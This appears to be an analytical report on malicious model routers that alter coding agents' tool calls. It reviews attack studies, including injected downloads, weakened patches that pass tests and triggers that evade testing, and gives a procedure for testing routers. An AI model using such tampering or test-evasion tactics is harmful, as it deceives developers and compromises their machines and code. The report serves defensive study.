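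Fu and colleagues excluded Claude Code's default mode, which asks a person to approve actions, because human decisions were outside the scope of a study of automated execution. The 0% therefore applies only to agents working without a human check. A developer who read every command would probably have stopped the download in the SQLFluff session, but might well have missed two swapped letters in a package name.

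Fu and colleagues ran Claude Code with DeepSeek-V4-Pro, DeepSeek-V4-Flash, Kimi-2.7 Code and Qwen3.6-Plus, replacing one whole response in each run. Claude Code didn't block an injected call with any of the four models.

In the same comparison, a developer who judged the sessions by whether the bug was fixed would usually have had no reason to look further. The share of tasks the agent completed successfully fell by 0.91 percentage points with either DeepSeek model, and by about 7.3 points with Kimi and Qwen. The average run grew by 0.30 to 2.13 turns.

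The playback cannot show whether the model would detect the altered call. In real use, the agent sends the altered call and its output back to the model with the rest of the conversation, and the model might respond that it never requested that command. But as Fu and colleagues define the procedure, every response except the altered one comes from the recording, so it cannot react to the change. Playback alone does not easily explain the longer runs in the comparison of models, so some of those responses may have been live, but Fu and colleagues do not report whether any model flagged the altered call.

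The narrow range of conditions is a serious concern, because there were only three tasks and each injection ran once on each. With so many runs and no blocked calls, the result is unlikely to be due to chance. Fu and colleagues say their figures depend on the configuration and may differ elsewhere, especially where an agent enforces stricter controls. They also gave each kind of attack the same number of samples to allow comparison, so the mix is not evidence of what malicious routers actually send. The main measure counts denials, so a command that ran and failed counts the same as one that ran and did damage.

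### What a passing test shows

Developers usually check an agent's work by running the project's tests. Luo and colleagues measured how often altered code passes those tests. They focused on subtle edits and excluded visible actions, such as destructive commands and dependency substitution.

The main experiment used bug reports about Django from SWE-bench Verified. Each task had public tests to check whether the agent had fixed the bug, and a hidden check for a particular security weakness, such as cross-site scripting or an authentication bypass. The router altered the agent's edit to introduce the weakness while trying to keep the fix working. This was reliably possible for 12 of the 18 Django issues, and running those 12 with five models gave 60 cases.

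Luo and colleagues repeated the experiment on APPS, a collection of programming problems, with 100 problems for each model.

| Benchmark and router | Passed the public tests | Failed the hidden security check |
|---|---|---|
| Django, honest router | 58.1% | 10.5% |
| Django, altering router | 51.7% | 69.0% |
| APPS, honest router | 65.4% | 0% |
| APPS, altering router | 62.4% | 99.7% of the solutions that passed the public tests |

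The Django figure of 69.0% needs care. In their introduction, Luo and colleagues write that the hidden check failed in 69.0% of cases "with public tests still passing". Their results contradict this, because the public tests passed in only 51.7% of the altered runs. Both things cannot have happened in 69.0% of them. They do not give a figure for the combination, but if the two percentages cover the same runs, it must lie within these limits:

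0.690 + 0.517 − 1 = 0.207 ≤ share that passed the tests and failed the security check ≤ 0.517

Between about 21% and 52% of the altered patches therefore looked like working fixes but were insecure. Even the lower figure would be a serious problem for a team that merges code whenever the tests pass.

The honest runs help show how much of this the router caused. Many patches failed the public tests even without interference, and the alteration lowered the pass rate by only 6.4 percentage points, from 58.1%. (The text of the study gives the honest pass rate as 61.0%, which would make the drop 9.3 points.) The hidden check also failed in 10.5% of the honest runs, so a patch can be insecure without an attacker. The experiment was small, with a single run per case, but the increase from 10.5% to 69.0% is too large for that uncertainty to explain (Luo and colleagues give a 95% confidence interval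 of 57.6% to 77.4%).

The rate would probably be lower for Django bugs in general, because the experiment left out the six issues where the researchers could not force a reliable edit. The results also varied with whether the models could complete the task. The hidden check failed in 80% to 100% of runs for the kinds of weakness where a model could do so, and in none for two kinds that were each represented by a single issue the models never solved.

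The APPS result does measure the combination directly. Of the altered solutions that passed the public tests, 99.7% failed the hidden check, so the public tests caught almost none of the alterations in code that otherwise worked. Since 62.4% of the altered runs passed the public tests, about 62% of all problems ended with a solution that appeared correct but had been weakened. The 99.7% covers only solutions that passed the public tests. Across all tasks, 72.6% failed the hidden check.

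This is unsurprising, because a passing test shows only that the program gave the expected result for the inputs the test tried. It does not show who wrote the code, or how the program behaves in cases that no test covers. The public tests for a bug fix concentrate on the bug. In the Django example, a test that checked whether the page still escaped untrusted text would have failed, no matter who had removed the escaping. Projects can catch some malicious edits by testing the protections they depend on most, but such tests cover only weaknesses that someone thought of in advance.

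Tests also check the code, not the developer's computer, so every test could still pass if an added tool call copied a private key. If the developer learns the test results from the agent's summary, that summary has also passed through the router. Running the tests on a separate build server gives a result that the router cannot rewrite, although the altered Django patch would have passed there too.

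### Agents that do other work

Luo and colleagues found the same weakness in agents with other tools when they tested five models on the Agent Security Bench (ASB), which covers ten roles in different fields. Altering the response redirected the agent to the attacker's action in 89.1% of tasks on average, ranging from 61.9% for Claude Opus 4.6 to 99.4% for MiniMax-M2.5. Refusals do not explain why Claude was redirected less often, since its refusal rate was 26.9%, compared with 53.8% for MiniMax.

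Direct prompt injection succeeded in 42.6% of the same tasks. Luo and colleagues caution against ranking the two attacks by these results, because only prompt injection has to overcome the model's training.

On AgentDojo, another benchmark without coding tasks, altered responses succeeded in 72.5% of 949 cases. The agent still completed the user's task in 50.3% of cases, compared with 11.4% under prompt injection. A user whose request fails will probably look for the cause, so a successful attack is most likely to go unnoticed when the agent also completes the user's task.

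## How often routers have been caught changing tool calls

Laboratory tests don't measure how many routers change tool calls, but two studies from 2026 looked for tampering in router services open to the public. Liu and colleagues found that nine of 428 routers put malicious code into tool calls. In *What the Middleman Delivers*, Wu, Zhao and colleagues (2026) confirmed no injection in the 20 they tested. The results don't conflict, because the researchers chose different kinds of router and sent them different tasks.

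There is little other field evidence. Of the router studies that Wu and colleagues compare with their own, only the one by Liu and colleagues tested for malicious edits. The others checked things like billing, speed and whether a router had delivered a cheaper model than it advertised.

### How Liu and colleagues tested 428 routers

The researchers bought access to 28 paid routers on the Chinese marketplaces Taobao and Xianyu and from online shops hosted by Shopify. They collected another 400 free routers from public communities. Crosley, working from the full paper, describes four stages of testing for each router:

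1. The researchers registered an account and obtained a credential.
2. They connected a coding agent to the router from inside a sandbox. The agent worked on a random selection of the researchers' own tasks and tasks from TerminalBench 2.0, a benchmark of command-line work. These tasks involve shell commands, package installations and file changes, so a malicious router had realistic tool calls to alter.
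3. They executed every tool call that came back and watched the sandbox for unexpected network connections, file changes and unusual processes.
4. A separate analysis agent reviewed the suspicious runs and classified each as benign rewriting, potentially malicious or confirmed malicious.

Liu and colleagues counted a router as injecting code only if it turned a tool call into a command or package that an attacker controlled. By that definition, one of the 28 paid routers and eight of the 400 free ones injected malicious code. Help Net Security reports the same numbers.

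The definition leaves out harmless reformatting, which many honest routers do. It also leaves out routers that only copy secrets. It seems to leave out subtle code edits that add no command or package, like the one Luo and colleagues made in Django, so a router that made only such edits could have passed this test.

Two of the nine routers acted only when a trigger was met, and other routers may have had triggers that the tests didn't set off, so nine should be treated as a minimum.

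The count could also include false positives. An automated reviewer made the final classification, and Crosley's account mentions no human check of its verdicts. With only nine positive cases, two or three mistakes would change the rate noticeably. But the strict definition makes such mistakes less likely, since it is fairly easy to confirm that a command fetches software from a stranger's server.

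### Which routers the count describes

The sample comes from the cheap, public end of the market. According to Crosley, most of the routers came from Chinese-language marketplaces and communities, and most of the free ones ran on one of two open-source templates, sub2api and new-api. Liu and colleagues left out enterprise and invite-only services. They discuss OpenRouter and LiteLLM as background but did not test either.

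*The Cost of Proxies* (2026), a commentary published the day after the paper, calls this a convenience sample drawn from the population most likely to have problems. It concludes that buyers can use the rate to judge the grey market, but not company gateways or well-known commercial services. That seems right, but it doesn't show that those other services are safe. Their rate could be much lower, but neither study measured it.

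The count also gives every router the same weight, regardless of how many people use it, so the 2% of free routers that injected code may have carried much more or much less than 2% of the traffic. According to *The Cost of Proxies*, the paper cites a survey that found some Taobao sellers have had more than 30,000 repeat purchases. One malicious seller of that size could do more damage than eight free routers with a few dozen users each.

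The routers may also not be independent. Tom's Hardware's *Chinese grey market sells Claude API access at 90 percent off* describes a supply chain in which upstream operators register accounts in bulk and most participants handle only one or two links. If several of the eight free routers bought access from the same supplier, that supplier could have made all of their changes, and the eight routers would represent fewer than eight separate attackers.

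### Twenty routers and no confirmed injection

Wu and colleagues, at Queen's University in Canada, studied routers that offered OpenAI's GPT-6 Astra, Anthropic's Claude Opus 5 or both. They asked ChatGPT, Claude, Gemini and Grok for recommendations, then added candidates from community lists, Hacker News and English-language web searches. To qualify, a service generally had to publish its prices, have an English interface and let individuals register. It also had to accept a credit card or PayPal, with a minimum deposit of $15 or less.

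These rules excluded much of the market that Liu and colleagues studied. They ruled out services that were free, had only a Chinese interface or took only cryptocurrency. In the first search, seven of 15 candidates met the conditions. In the final sample, ten routers charged less than the official price, nine charged about the same and one charged more.

For each model at each router, the researchers scheduled 50 requests for code or setup instructions. The requests covered package names, shell commands, web addresses, encoded content and installation steps, where injected code would be most useful to an attacker. The researchers sent the same requests to the official services for comparison. Software flagged responses that contained misspelt package names, unexpected domains, potentially harmful commands or encoded text, and two of the researchers examined each flagged response in context.

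The first round, in early October 2026, produced 1,686 responses from the routers. The software flagged 48 of them, along with 16 official responses, and the reviewers judged all 64 to be benign. Some mentioned legitimate packages that suited the task, and the screening software had flagged others by mistake. The second round, 11 to 18 days later, added 1,646 responses, and the software flagged 43 of them.

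The reviewers initially disagreed about three of those 43. Each of the three suggested installing scikit-learn, a common Python library, to load a standard dataset. An official response had already made the same kind of suggestion, so the reviewers classified all three as benign. Without responses from the official service, a reviewer might have mistaken an optional package like this for an injected one.

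In total, there were no confirmed injections in 3,332 responses. The first-round counts include no screened responses from one of the 20 routers, labelled R05. The second-round total is also about what 50 requests to each retested combination of router and model would produce, excluding R05. The injection result is therefore probably based on 19 routers rather than 20.

Some routers also restricted which programs could connect. R04 offered Astra only to an unmodified version of the official client, so the researchers tested it separately through that client and found nothing suspicious in 50 responses. By the second round, R13 accepted Opus requests only from a particular coding program. The researchers did not try to get around this and left R13 out of that round.

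### Tool calls that the request had disabled

Although Wu and colleagues found no malicious code, several routers returned tool calls that should not have been there. The requests to Opus declared a tool called `noop`, which the researchers never intended to use, and set `tool_choice` to `none`, which forbids the model to call any tool. In the first round, four routers returned calls to `noop` anyway:

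| Router | Price compared with the official service | Forbidden calls, round one | Forbidden calls, round two |
|---|---|---|---|
| R11 | Lower | 24 | 0 |
| R17 | Lower | 4 | 0 |
| R04 | Lower | 1 | 0 |
| R10 | About the same | 1 | 0 |

A fifth router, R08, returned two web-search calls in response to Astra requests that offered no tools. The official services returned no tool calls in either round.

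The researchers could not tell where the forbidden calls came from. A router might have added them, removed the restriction before forwarding the request, or made a mistake converting the response between formats. An upstream service might also have ignored the restriction. R10's responses suggest a fairly innocent explanation. Wu and colleagues think R10 wraps each request in instructions meant for a coding program, and these could have interfered with the restriction. The responses referred to disabled tools, and R10 reported a median of about 59,500 more input tokens than the official service did for identical requests.

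Nothing in these calls points to an attack. They named a tool that the researchers had declared themselves and had no use for, and the study reports no attacker-controlled command in any of them. However, an agent that relies on the request to keep its tools switched off might execute whatever call comes back. Wu and colleagues recommend that the user's own program reject any call the request did not permit.

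The counts can't be used to calculate a rate of violations. They include calls returned during failed attempts, and 24 of the 30 `noop` calls came from one router. A router's behaviour can also change quickly. R11 returned 24 forbidden calls on October 5 and none on October 20, so a user who tested it only on October 20 would have seen nothing wrong.

A router that injects no malicious code may still deliver something other than what the user paid for. Five routers reported between 4,200 and 60,000 more input tokens than the official services did for identical requests, which could mean that they had added hidden instructions or that they had counted tokens differently. Seven of the ten cheaper routers differed in accuracy from the official model, compared with two of the ten that charged the official price or more. That gap between the price groups could still be chance (p = 0.07), and the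 results do not show why accuracy differed.

### Why the two results are compatible

The most important difference between the studies is the kind of responses the routers handled. Liu and colleagues ran a coding agent, so the responses contained shell commands and package installations in the form that an agent executes. Wu and colleagues sent separate requests and looked for malicious additions in the answers. The official services returned no tool calls to the same requests, so the routers probably had no genuine tool call to rewrite. A router built to change agents' shell commands could have forwarded all 3,332 responses unchanged.

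Wu and colleagues acknowledge that their requests involved no executed tools, secrets or long conversations, any of which a router might wait for before acting. They write that their result is compatible with attacks found in other settings, but that the studies differ too much to combine their rates.

The studies also handled the returned commands differently. Running a command in a sandbox can reveal harm that isn't apparent from its text, such as an ordinary-looking installation that contacts an attacker's server. Wu and colleagues ran no commands, so they relied on their software to flag malicious responses, and they did not measure what share it would catch. Their reviewers read only the flagged responses, so an injection the software missed would have counted as clean.

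The two studies also tested different kinds of routers. Eight of the nine that Liu and colleagues caught were free, and Wu and colleagues tested no free routers. Services that publish prices and accept credit cards may also attract fewer dishonest operators, because it is harder to stay anonymous while running one. This explanation is a guess, since neither study compared routers that differed only in how they took payment.

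Price alone is unlikely to explain the difference. Half of the routers Wu and colleagues tested were cheaper than the official service, and none of those produced a confirmed injection either. Liu and colleagues found one injecting router among the paid services, which is too little evidence to show whether paid routers are safer than free ones.

### How uncertain the rates are

Even a perfectly random sample can contain too many or too few malicious routers by chance. A 95% interval gives the range of true rates that are reasonably compatible with the count. Standard binomial calculations give these results:

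| Sample | Routers that injected code | Share | 95% interval |
|---|---|---|---|
| Free routers, Liu and colleagues | 8 of 400 | 2.0% | 0.9% to 3.9% |
| Paid routers, Liu and colleagues | 1 of 28 | 3.6% | 0.1% to 18% |
| Routers in Wu and colleagues | 0 of 20 | 0% | 0% to 14% |

The estimate for free routers is by far the most precise, because there were 400 of them. The paid rate looks higher, but its interval runs from about one malicious router in a thousand to nearly one in five, which contains the whole interval for the free routers.

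The upper limit for Wu and colleagues is simple to derive. If a share *p* of all routers inject code, the chance that 20 randomly chosen routers include none is (1 − *p*)²⁰. The limit is the value of *p* at which this chance falls to 5%:

(1 − *p*)²⁰ = 0.05, so *p* = 1 − 0.05^(1/20) ≈ 0.139

Finding no malicious routers among 20 is therefore compatible with a true rate of up to about 14%, or about 15% with 19 routers.

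Wu and colleagues report a much smaller upper limit of 0.09%, but it applies to responses rather than routers. If each response were independent, fewer than about one in a thousand responses to these requests would contain an injection that their method could confirm. Responses from the same router are not independent, though, because one operator decides how that router treats all of them. Somebody choosing a new router needs to know how many operators are dishonest, and thousands of responses from 20 operators can't narrow that down much.

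Finding no malicious routers in a sample of 20 is unsurprising. If 2% of routers injected code, 20 random routers would include none that did so about 67% of the time (0.98²⁰ ≈ 0.67). The 28 paid routers are a closer match for this sample, and at their rate of 3.6%, a study of 20 would still find none nearly half the time. Researchers would need to test 149 randomly chosen routers and find no injection to put the rate below 2% with 95% confidence.

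These calculations all assume random samples of routers, but neither group sampled at random. Liu and colleagues collected routers that were on sale or publicly posted in particular communities. Wu and colleagues set criteria for including routers, then added more cheap services after early results. The intervals account for chance in sampling but not for a bias towards one kind of router. If some routers share suppliers, the true uncertainty is larger still.

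A reasonable estimate is that about one in 50 free public routers of the kind Liu and colleagues tested were visibly injecting code in early 2026. One person's risk can be higher, because people who rely on free routers may go through several as services fail or run out of credit. If the risks were independent, someone who tried ten would have about an 18% chance of using at least one that injects code (1 − 0.98¹⁰ ≈ 0.18). No comparable estimate exists for company gateways or large commercial services.

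### The claims of 26 routers and a $500,000 loss

The paper documents nine routers injecting malicious tool calls, but some of the publicity for the study reported larger numbers. Chaofan Shou, one of the paper's authors, claimed in a post on X that 26 routers were "secretly injecting malicious tool calls and stealing creds". He also claimed that one router had drained a client's wallet of $500,000. *AI agents in crypto expose a hidden router risk*, a news article that quotes the post, says the researchers documented 26 routers injecting malicious tool calls.

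The number 26 probably comes from adding those nine routers to the 17 that led to someone using an Amazon credential the researchers had planted. The sum is correct only if no router did both. All 17 were free, as were eight of the nine that injected code, so up to eight routers could be in both groups, which would leave between 18 and 26 different routers. Shou's wording can be read as a total for both behaviours, but it is easy to misread as 26 routers that all changed tool calls.

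Risky Bulletin's *Malicious LLM proxy routers found in the wild* makes a different mistake. It counts 28 malicious routers by adding the nine that injected code, the two with triggers and the 17 connected to the Amazon credentials. This counts the two with triggers twice, because they were already among the nine. The study also included 28 paid routers, so a reader could think that every paid router was malicious.

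The headline of BlockBeats' *Solayer Founder Reveals LLM Supply Chain Major Security Flaw* states that over 20% of free routers are exposed to malicious injection, but the article gives the correct count of eight in 400, or 2%.

The $500,000 loss claimed in Shou's post is harder to assess. The paper describes a router that drained an Ethereum wallet, but the wallet belonged to the researchers, who had put money in it as bait. Crosley reports, citing the appendix, that this loss was under $50. Neither the paper's abstract nor Crosley's detailed account of the full text mentions a client who lost money.

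Shou may have been describing a separate incident. According to *The Cost of Proxies*, the authors' affiliations include two companies, Fuzzland and World Liberty Financial, and two University of California campuses. An author could have learned of a client's loss through commercial work, and there would have been no reason to include it in a study that used planted keys. But the post alone does not establish that the loss happened or that a router caused it.

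Anyone can see transfers on a public blockchain, so others could confirm the amount and date of the loss if they had the wallet's address. Connecting the loss to a router would require more evidence, such as records showing that the wallet's key had passed through the router and had not leaked elsewhere.

The OECD's *Malicious AI Routers Enable Cryptocurrency and Credential Theft* (2026), an AI-generated entry in its incident monitor, says that malicious routers resulted in "real cryptocurrency theft". Someone did take the money in the bait wallet, but the entry describes the same research, so it is not separate support for the larger claim.

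The $500,000 loss, even if confirmed, may not have involved payload injection, because a thief who has copied a wallet's private key can empty the wallet without changing any tool call.

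## Testing a router that may behave well while it is being tested

Two of the nine routers that Liu and colleagues caught injecting code had triggers, so a developer who tried either one with a few harmless requests would probably have found nothing wrong. A useful test has to create conditions in which a router might misbehave, then run long enough to see it happen.

### The triggers researchers have observed

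Both routers were free services. Crosley, quoting the full paper, reports that one injected malicious tool calls only after the first 50 requests. The other acted only when the session appeared to run under auto-approval and the project appeared to be written in Rust or Go.

Attackers have an obvious reason to target auto-approved sessions, but it is unknown why the second router also required the project to be in Rust or Go. The router could easily have recognised such projects from their file names and build commands.

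Liu and colleagues had to infer both conditions from the sessions in which altered calls appeared. Crosley does not make clear whether the first router counted requests per account or per conversation, so a test should allow for either.

Liu and colleagues list five families of trigger. The two routers they caught are examples of the request-count and user-trait families. Each family calls for something different from a test:

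| What the trigger depends on | What the test has to include | What a clean result leaves open |
|---|---|---|
| The tool the model calls | Every tool the agent uses in real work, including package installation | Tools that the test never called |
| Keywords in the conversation | Tasks and files that resemble the team's own | Subjects that never came up |
| Traits of the user or session | Each permission setting, programming language and agent program in use | Settings and projects outside the test |
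| Time | Sessions at different hours and on different days | Every period without a test |
| The number of requests | One account in continuous use, and some long conversations | Anything beyond the longest run |

A router may also require several conditions at once, like the one that activated only when auto-approval was on and the project used Rust or Go. If a tester tried auto-approval on a Python project, then manual approval on a Rust project, that router would leave the tool calls unchanged in both sessions. To detect such a router, the tester has to test combinations of settings.

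### How to run the test

The procedure below builds on the one Liu and colleagues used. It is for a team that has a reason to use a particular router and wants to check it for tampering first.

1. Set up a disposable virtual machine with no real code, passwords or keys on it, and no access to the internal network. Some sessions will run commands without approval, so the tester should assume that a malicious one will run. The router account should have a spending limit.
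2. Install the agent program that the developers use, in the same version and with the same settings. Routers can tell programs apart. Two of the services that Wu and colleagues studied accepted certain requests only from a particular program, so a test script might not receive the same treatment as a real agent.
3. Give the agent ordinary work on copies of public projects, such as fixing a bug, adding a dependency or setting up a build. Liu and colleagues mixed their own tasks with a public benchmark. The mixture is sensible because an operator could learn to recognise a well-known benchmark.
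4. Run each type of project under each permission setting that developers use, including auto-approval if anyone uses it.
5. Stay on one account well past 50 requests, and let some conversations grow long. Opening a new account for each batch could restart the router's count.
6. Let the commands run, and record network connections, changed files and new processes as well as the raw responses. Software can sort out the calls most worth reading, though it misses some altered ones.
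7. Repeat the test after a few weeks, at a different time of day, and whenever the operator announces a new upstream.

Before drawing a conclusion from a suspicious call, the reviewer should check whether the package, domain or command makes sense for the task, and whether the official service ever suggests the same thing. If the command clearly fetches an attacker's software, one example is enough reason to stop using the router. Repeating the session without seeing the command again doesn't show that the router is safe, because the condition that triggered the rewrite may no longer hold.

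Even a careful test differs from real use because the machine contains no valuable secrets, the account is new, and the projects are public. A tester can execute tools and hold long conversations, which Wu and colleagues did not do, but putting real secrets on the machine would create the risk the test is meant to measure. Planted keys are a partial substitute, although an operator who tries one may discover that it's worthless.

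### How many calls and sessions are enough

Suppose a router alters a share *p* of eligible calls, meaning the calls it would consider altering, and decides about each one independently. The calculation used for the sample of 20 routers then gives the number of calls *n* needed for a 95% chance of seeing an altered one:

(1 − *p*)ⁿ = 0.05, so *n* = ln(0.05) / ln(1 − *p*)

At *p* = 1%, the formula gives 298.1, so the tester needs 299 calls. For small shares, 3/*p* is a good approximation.

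| Share of eligible calls altered | Eligible calls for a 95% chance of seeing one |
|---|---|
| 50% | 5 |
| 10% | 29 |
| 5% | 59 |
| 1% | 299 |
| 0.1% | 2,995 |

If a router alters only package installations, and one tool call in ten installs a package, a tester needs about 2,990 calls to collect 299 eligible ones. A tester can collect them with far fewer calls by choosing tasks with many installations and downloads than by running more sessions of file reading.

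The 95% is the chance of catching a router that alters calls at the stated rate, not the chance that a router with a clean result never alters calls. A router that altered one eligible call in a thousand would pass a 299-call test about 74% of the time (0.999²⁹⁹ ≈ 0.74). An agent can make hundreds of calls in one turn, so a busy team could still receive an altered command every few days.

The formula also assumes that the router can alter calls throughout the test. A router that waits 50 requests before acting can't be revealed by a ten-request test, however often the tester repeats it on new accounts. To test for a router that waits 50 requests and then alters 1% of eligible calls, the tester has to send 50 requests and then as many more as it takes to collect 299 eligible calls.

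Whether a test outlasts a router's delay also depends on how the router counts requests. In each round, Wu and colleagues scheduled 50 requests for code or setup instructions and 135 knowledge questions for each combination of router and model. A 50-request delay would have ended during the round if the router counted all 185 requests together, but never if it restarted the count with each conversation, because each request was a separate conversation.

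For triggers that depend on the session, the tester should count sessions instead of calls, because extra calls in a session that doesn't meet the conditions can't set off the trigger. If a tester picks each session's programming language at random from ten, including Rust and Go, and uses auto-approval half the time, the chance that a session meets the second router's conditions is 0.2 × 0.5 = 0.1. If the router always acts when the conditions are met, the tester needs 29 sessions for a 95% chance of catching it.

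A planned test does better than a random one. Ten languages and two permission settings make 20 combinations, and running each combination once guarantees two sessions that match the trigger. But if the tester leaves out the relevant language or setting, the chance of detection is zero no matter how many sessions they run.

If the router alters only some calls in a matching session, the two calculations combine. Let *q* be the share of sessions that meet the conditions and *m* the number of eligible calls in each. The chance that one session reveals the router is

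*d* = *q* × [1 − (1 − *p*)ᵐ]

With *q* = 10%, *p* = 1% and *m* = 50, *d* is about 3.9%, and replacing *p* with *d* in the first formula gives 75 sessions. A company choosing a supplier could still run that many, but it's far more work than most people would do before trying a free router.

### Why there is no original to compare with

Comparing each response with the one the provider sent would make testing easier, but the tester sees only what the router delivers. Sending the same request directly to the provider doesn't recover the original response, because a model's answers vary. Miao, Huang and colleagues (2026), in *Is Your LLM Relay Serving What It Claims?*, give two reasons: a model's output is usually partly random, and the provider's serving system adds further variation.

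A coding agent makes the problem worse. One run might read a test file first while another searches the project, so the two conversations contain different information and lead to different commands. A package name that appears only in the run through the router could have been injected, or it could be part of another reasonable way to do the task.

Earlier researchers had an easier time testing Tor, an anonymity network that sends a user's traffic through a chain of volunteers' computers. The last computer in the chain, the exit relay, passes the traffic on to the ordinary internet. It can read and change any traffic that isn't end-to-end encrypted, so its position is similar to a router's. Winter and Lindskog (2014), in *Spoiled Onions*, built a scanner, exitmap, to look for exit relays that tampered with traffic.

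Their scanner compared what came back through each relay with answers the researchers already knew. One check requested a website's security certificate through each relay and compared the certificate's fingerprint with the correct one, which the researchers had stored in advance. Another fetched pages known to contain encrypted links and looked for relays that had changed them to unencrypted ones. An older scanner, begun in 2006, fetched decoy content once through Tor and once directly, then compared the two copies. Someone testing an open web proxy could do the same with any page that doesn't change.

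The method was less reliable when honest relays could return different answers. Winter and Lindskog also checked whether relays returned the right internet addresses for domain names, but large websites use many addresses that differ by region, so an unexpected address was weak evidence of tampering. Almost all language model responses have the same problem, because the same request can produce different responses even when the router is honest.

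*Identifying and characterizing Sybils in the Tor network* (2016) reports that exitmap, using a fixed comparison, exposed 251 malicious exit relays between August 2014 and January 2016. The paper also notes that the tampering might have happened upstream of the relay, for example at a malicious network operator. Tests of routers face the same difficulty.

Winter and Lindskog worried about relays that would attack only connections that looked genuine. They made the scanner's opening message match the Tor Browser's and avoided connecting to exit relays directly, since a relay could detect that such a connection came from outside the Tor network and not attack it. They also hoped that many volunteers would run the scanner, so that relay operators couldn't learn to recognise one testing machine.

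Router testers can copy the first precaution by using a real agent. Spreading the test across many people makes the tester harder to recognise but gives each account fewer requests. If ten volunteers each send 30 requests from their own accounts, a router that waits for 50 requests per account before rewriting tool calls will pass all ten tests, so each volunteer needs to run a long test.

A certificate check also has an advantage over a router test because it collects its evidence immediately. Winter and Lindskog point out that a relay's operator may become suspicious when a visitor fetches a certificate and then leaves, but by then the scanner already has its evidence. A short router test finds nothing if the router waits before it starts rewriting tool calls.

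The Tor Project could also act centrally on reports of bad exit relays. It tried to reproduce the reported attack and could then mark the relay in a signed list that every Tor program downloads. Within three hours, users' software stopped choosing that relay as an exit. Routers have no such shared list, and Wu and colleagues anonymised the services they measured, so a developer can't look up whether someone else has already caught a particular router.

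Testers can get something close to a fixed original tool call in two ways. A company that runs its own gateway can point it at a dummy provider that always returns the same tool calls, then compare what goes in with what comes out. This tests the gateway's software but not any router further upstream, and compromised software might behave differently with a dummy provider. With somebody else's router, the tester can ask the model to run one exact, harmless command and check whether that command arrives. Models usually comply, so a different domain or package would stand out. Such requests don't look much like normal work, so they should supplement realistic sessions rather than replace them.

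### What an audit of the model's identity can show

Researchers can compare how often an endpoint gives each possible answer, rather than comparing single responses. Audits of model identity do this to find routers that advertise one model and deliver a cheaper one. The audits work well for that purpose, and some are cheap enough to run regularly. But a router can deliver the advertised model and still rewrite the model's commands, as Fu and colleagues' experiments illustrate.

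*AgentProv* (Wang, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) identifies a model by which tool it picks when offered several that do the same job, such as three ways to create a calendar entry. These choices differ between models. A full audit runs 20 such tasks 50 times each, and the 1,000 requests typically cost well under a dollar in total.

The shares with which an endpoint picks each tool form its fingerprint, written as a vector φ. AgentProv measures the squared distance between the official endpoint's fingerprint and the router's:

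*T* = ‖φ<sub>official</sub> − φ<sub>router</sub>‖²

To decide whether *T* is large, AgentProv pools the two sets of answers within each task, splits them at random and recalculates the distance. It does this 1,000 times and flags the router if the real distance is larger than 95% of the recalculated ones.

In tests on 36 openly available models, this flagged all 630 pairs of different models and never flagged a model compared with itself. Many services add hidden instructions to requests. When Wang and colleagues added such instructions to requests sent to genuine models, AgentProv raised one false alarm in 15 tests (7%), while two older methods that compare text raised ten and eight.

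AgentProv is weak against payload injection because it records the tool's name in each answer but discards the arguments. A router can change the download address in every shell command without changing the tool's name, so the recorded answers, φ<sub>router</sub> and *T* all stay the same.

A router that changes tool names only occasionally is also hard to catch. Let φ′ be the fingerprint the router would have if it changed every call. If it changes a share *p*, then apart from sampling noise

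φ<sub>router</sub> = (1 − *p*) φ<sub>official</sub> + *p* φ′, so *T* = *p*² ‖φ<sub>official</sub> − φ′‖²

At *p* = 1%, the distance is one ten-thousandth of what it would be if the router changed every call. In one of Wang and colleagues' own tests of partial substitution, AgentProv raised no alarm when the smaller GPT-5.4-mini answered 60% of the requests meant for GPT-5.4.

AgentProv also accepted all nine OpenAI models that the researchers reached through OpenRouter. This is good evidence that OpenRouter delivered the models it advertised on that route. Nobody compared the arguments of the tool calls, so the result does not show whether they arrived intact.

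Miao and colleagues propose an even cheaper method, distributional fingerprint auditing. The auditor asks for simple choices, such as a letter, number or colour from a list, because different models favour different answers. The auditor asks five questions 50 times each and compares the counts with a stored record of 1,000 official answers per question. A chi-squared test, a standard way to compare counts, gives a result for each question, and another formula combines the five results into a single p-value.

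Miao and colleagues tested this on 240 pairs of an advertised model and a substitute, drawn from 16 models. They report detailed success rates for four advertised models, and the audit reached the right verdict more than 99.5% of the time for each. One audit of these models cost between $0.003 and $0.048. Building the official record, which later audits can reuse, cost at most another $0.96.

The method is much more sensitive to changed settings than you would expect from its accuracy. When Miao and colleagues kept DeepSeek's model but asked it to answer in a certain style or format, the audit flagged it in at least 99% of runs. A flagged router may therefore have added instructions to the request without replacing the model, which is a different problem, though a user might object to it too.

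Its formal hypothesis shows why a router can pass and still change commands. If *Q* is the set of audit questions, a router counts as consistent when

*P*<sub>router</sub>(answer | *x*) = *P*<sub>official</sub>(answer | *x*) for every question *x* in *Q*

The audit covers only *Q*. Its five questions ask for text, so a router has no shell command or package installation to rewrite. A router that altered every installation command could still forward all 250 answers unchanged and satisfy the hypothesis. Running more audits would only confirm that it leaves the answers to these five questions unchanged. Miao and colleagues acknowledge that a router may recognise audit questions and treat them differently from ordinary traffic.

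Results also go out of date. Wu and colleagues ran their own comparison, based on the accuracy of answers to knowledge questions, and repeated it in their second round. Of the 35 combinations of router and model that they retested, seven gained or lost a warning. One router, R02, had matched the official GPT-6 Astra in the first round. In the second, some of its answers described the 2025 Nobel Prize in Literature and Super Bowl LX as future events, which suggests that an older model was handling part of the traffic. Some of the other changes were small enough to be measurement noise, and the researchers did not measure how often a warning would appear or disappear without any change at the router.

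Failing an identity audit may still be a useful warning about tool calls. In the first round, Wu and colleagues flagged nine of their 20 routers for differences in accuracy, including all five that returned tool calls the request had not allowed. If the two problems were unrelated, all five would fall among the nine only about 0.8% of the time (9/20 × 8/19 × 7/18 × 6/17 × 5/16). The pattern emerged after the fact from a small sample, none of the five returned a confirmed injection, and Wu and colleagues caution that their findings do not establish a shared cause. Still, if a router fails a test that costs a few cents, a developer has a good reason to choose another one before starting a test that takes days.

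## Blocking dangerous tool calls before they run

A team that can't tell whether a router can be trusted can still check every tool call on its own machine before the agent runs it. Triggers can keep altered calls out of a test, but they do little to defeat local checks, which cover every call, including the first one altered after months of normal service.

Developers can approve calls by hand, enforce fixed rules, screen for unusual calls, have a second model review them, or run them in a sandbox. All of these controls work from the call that arrived, without a copy of the call the model produced.

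### Asking a person

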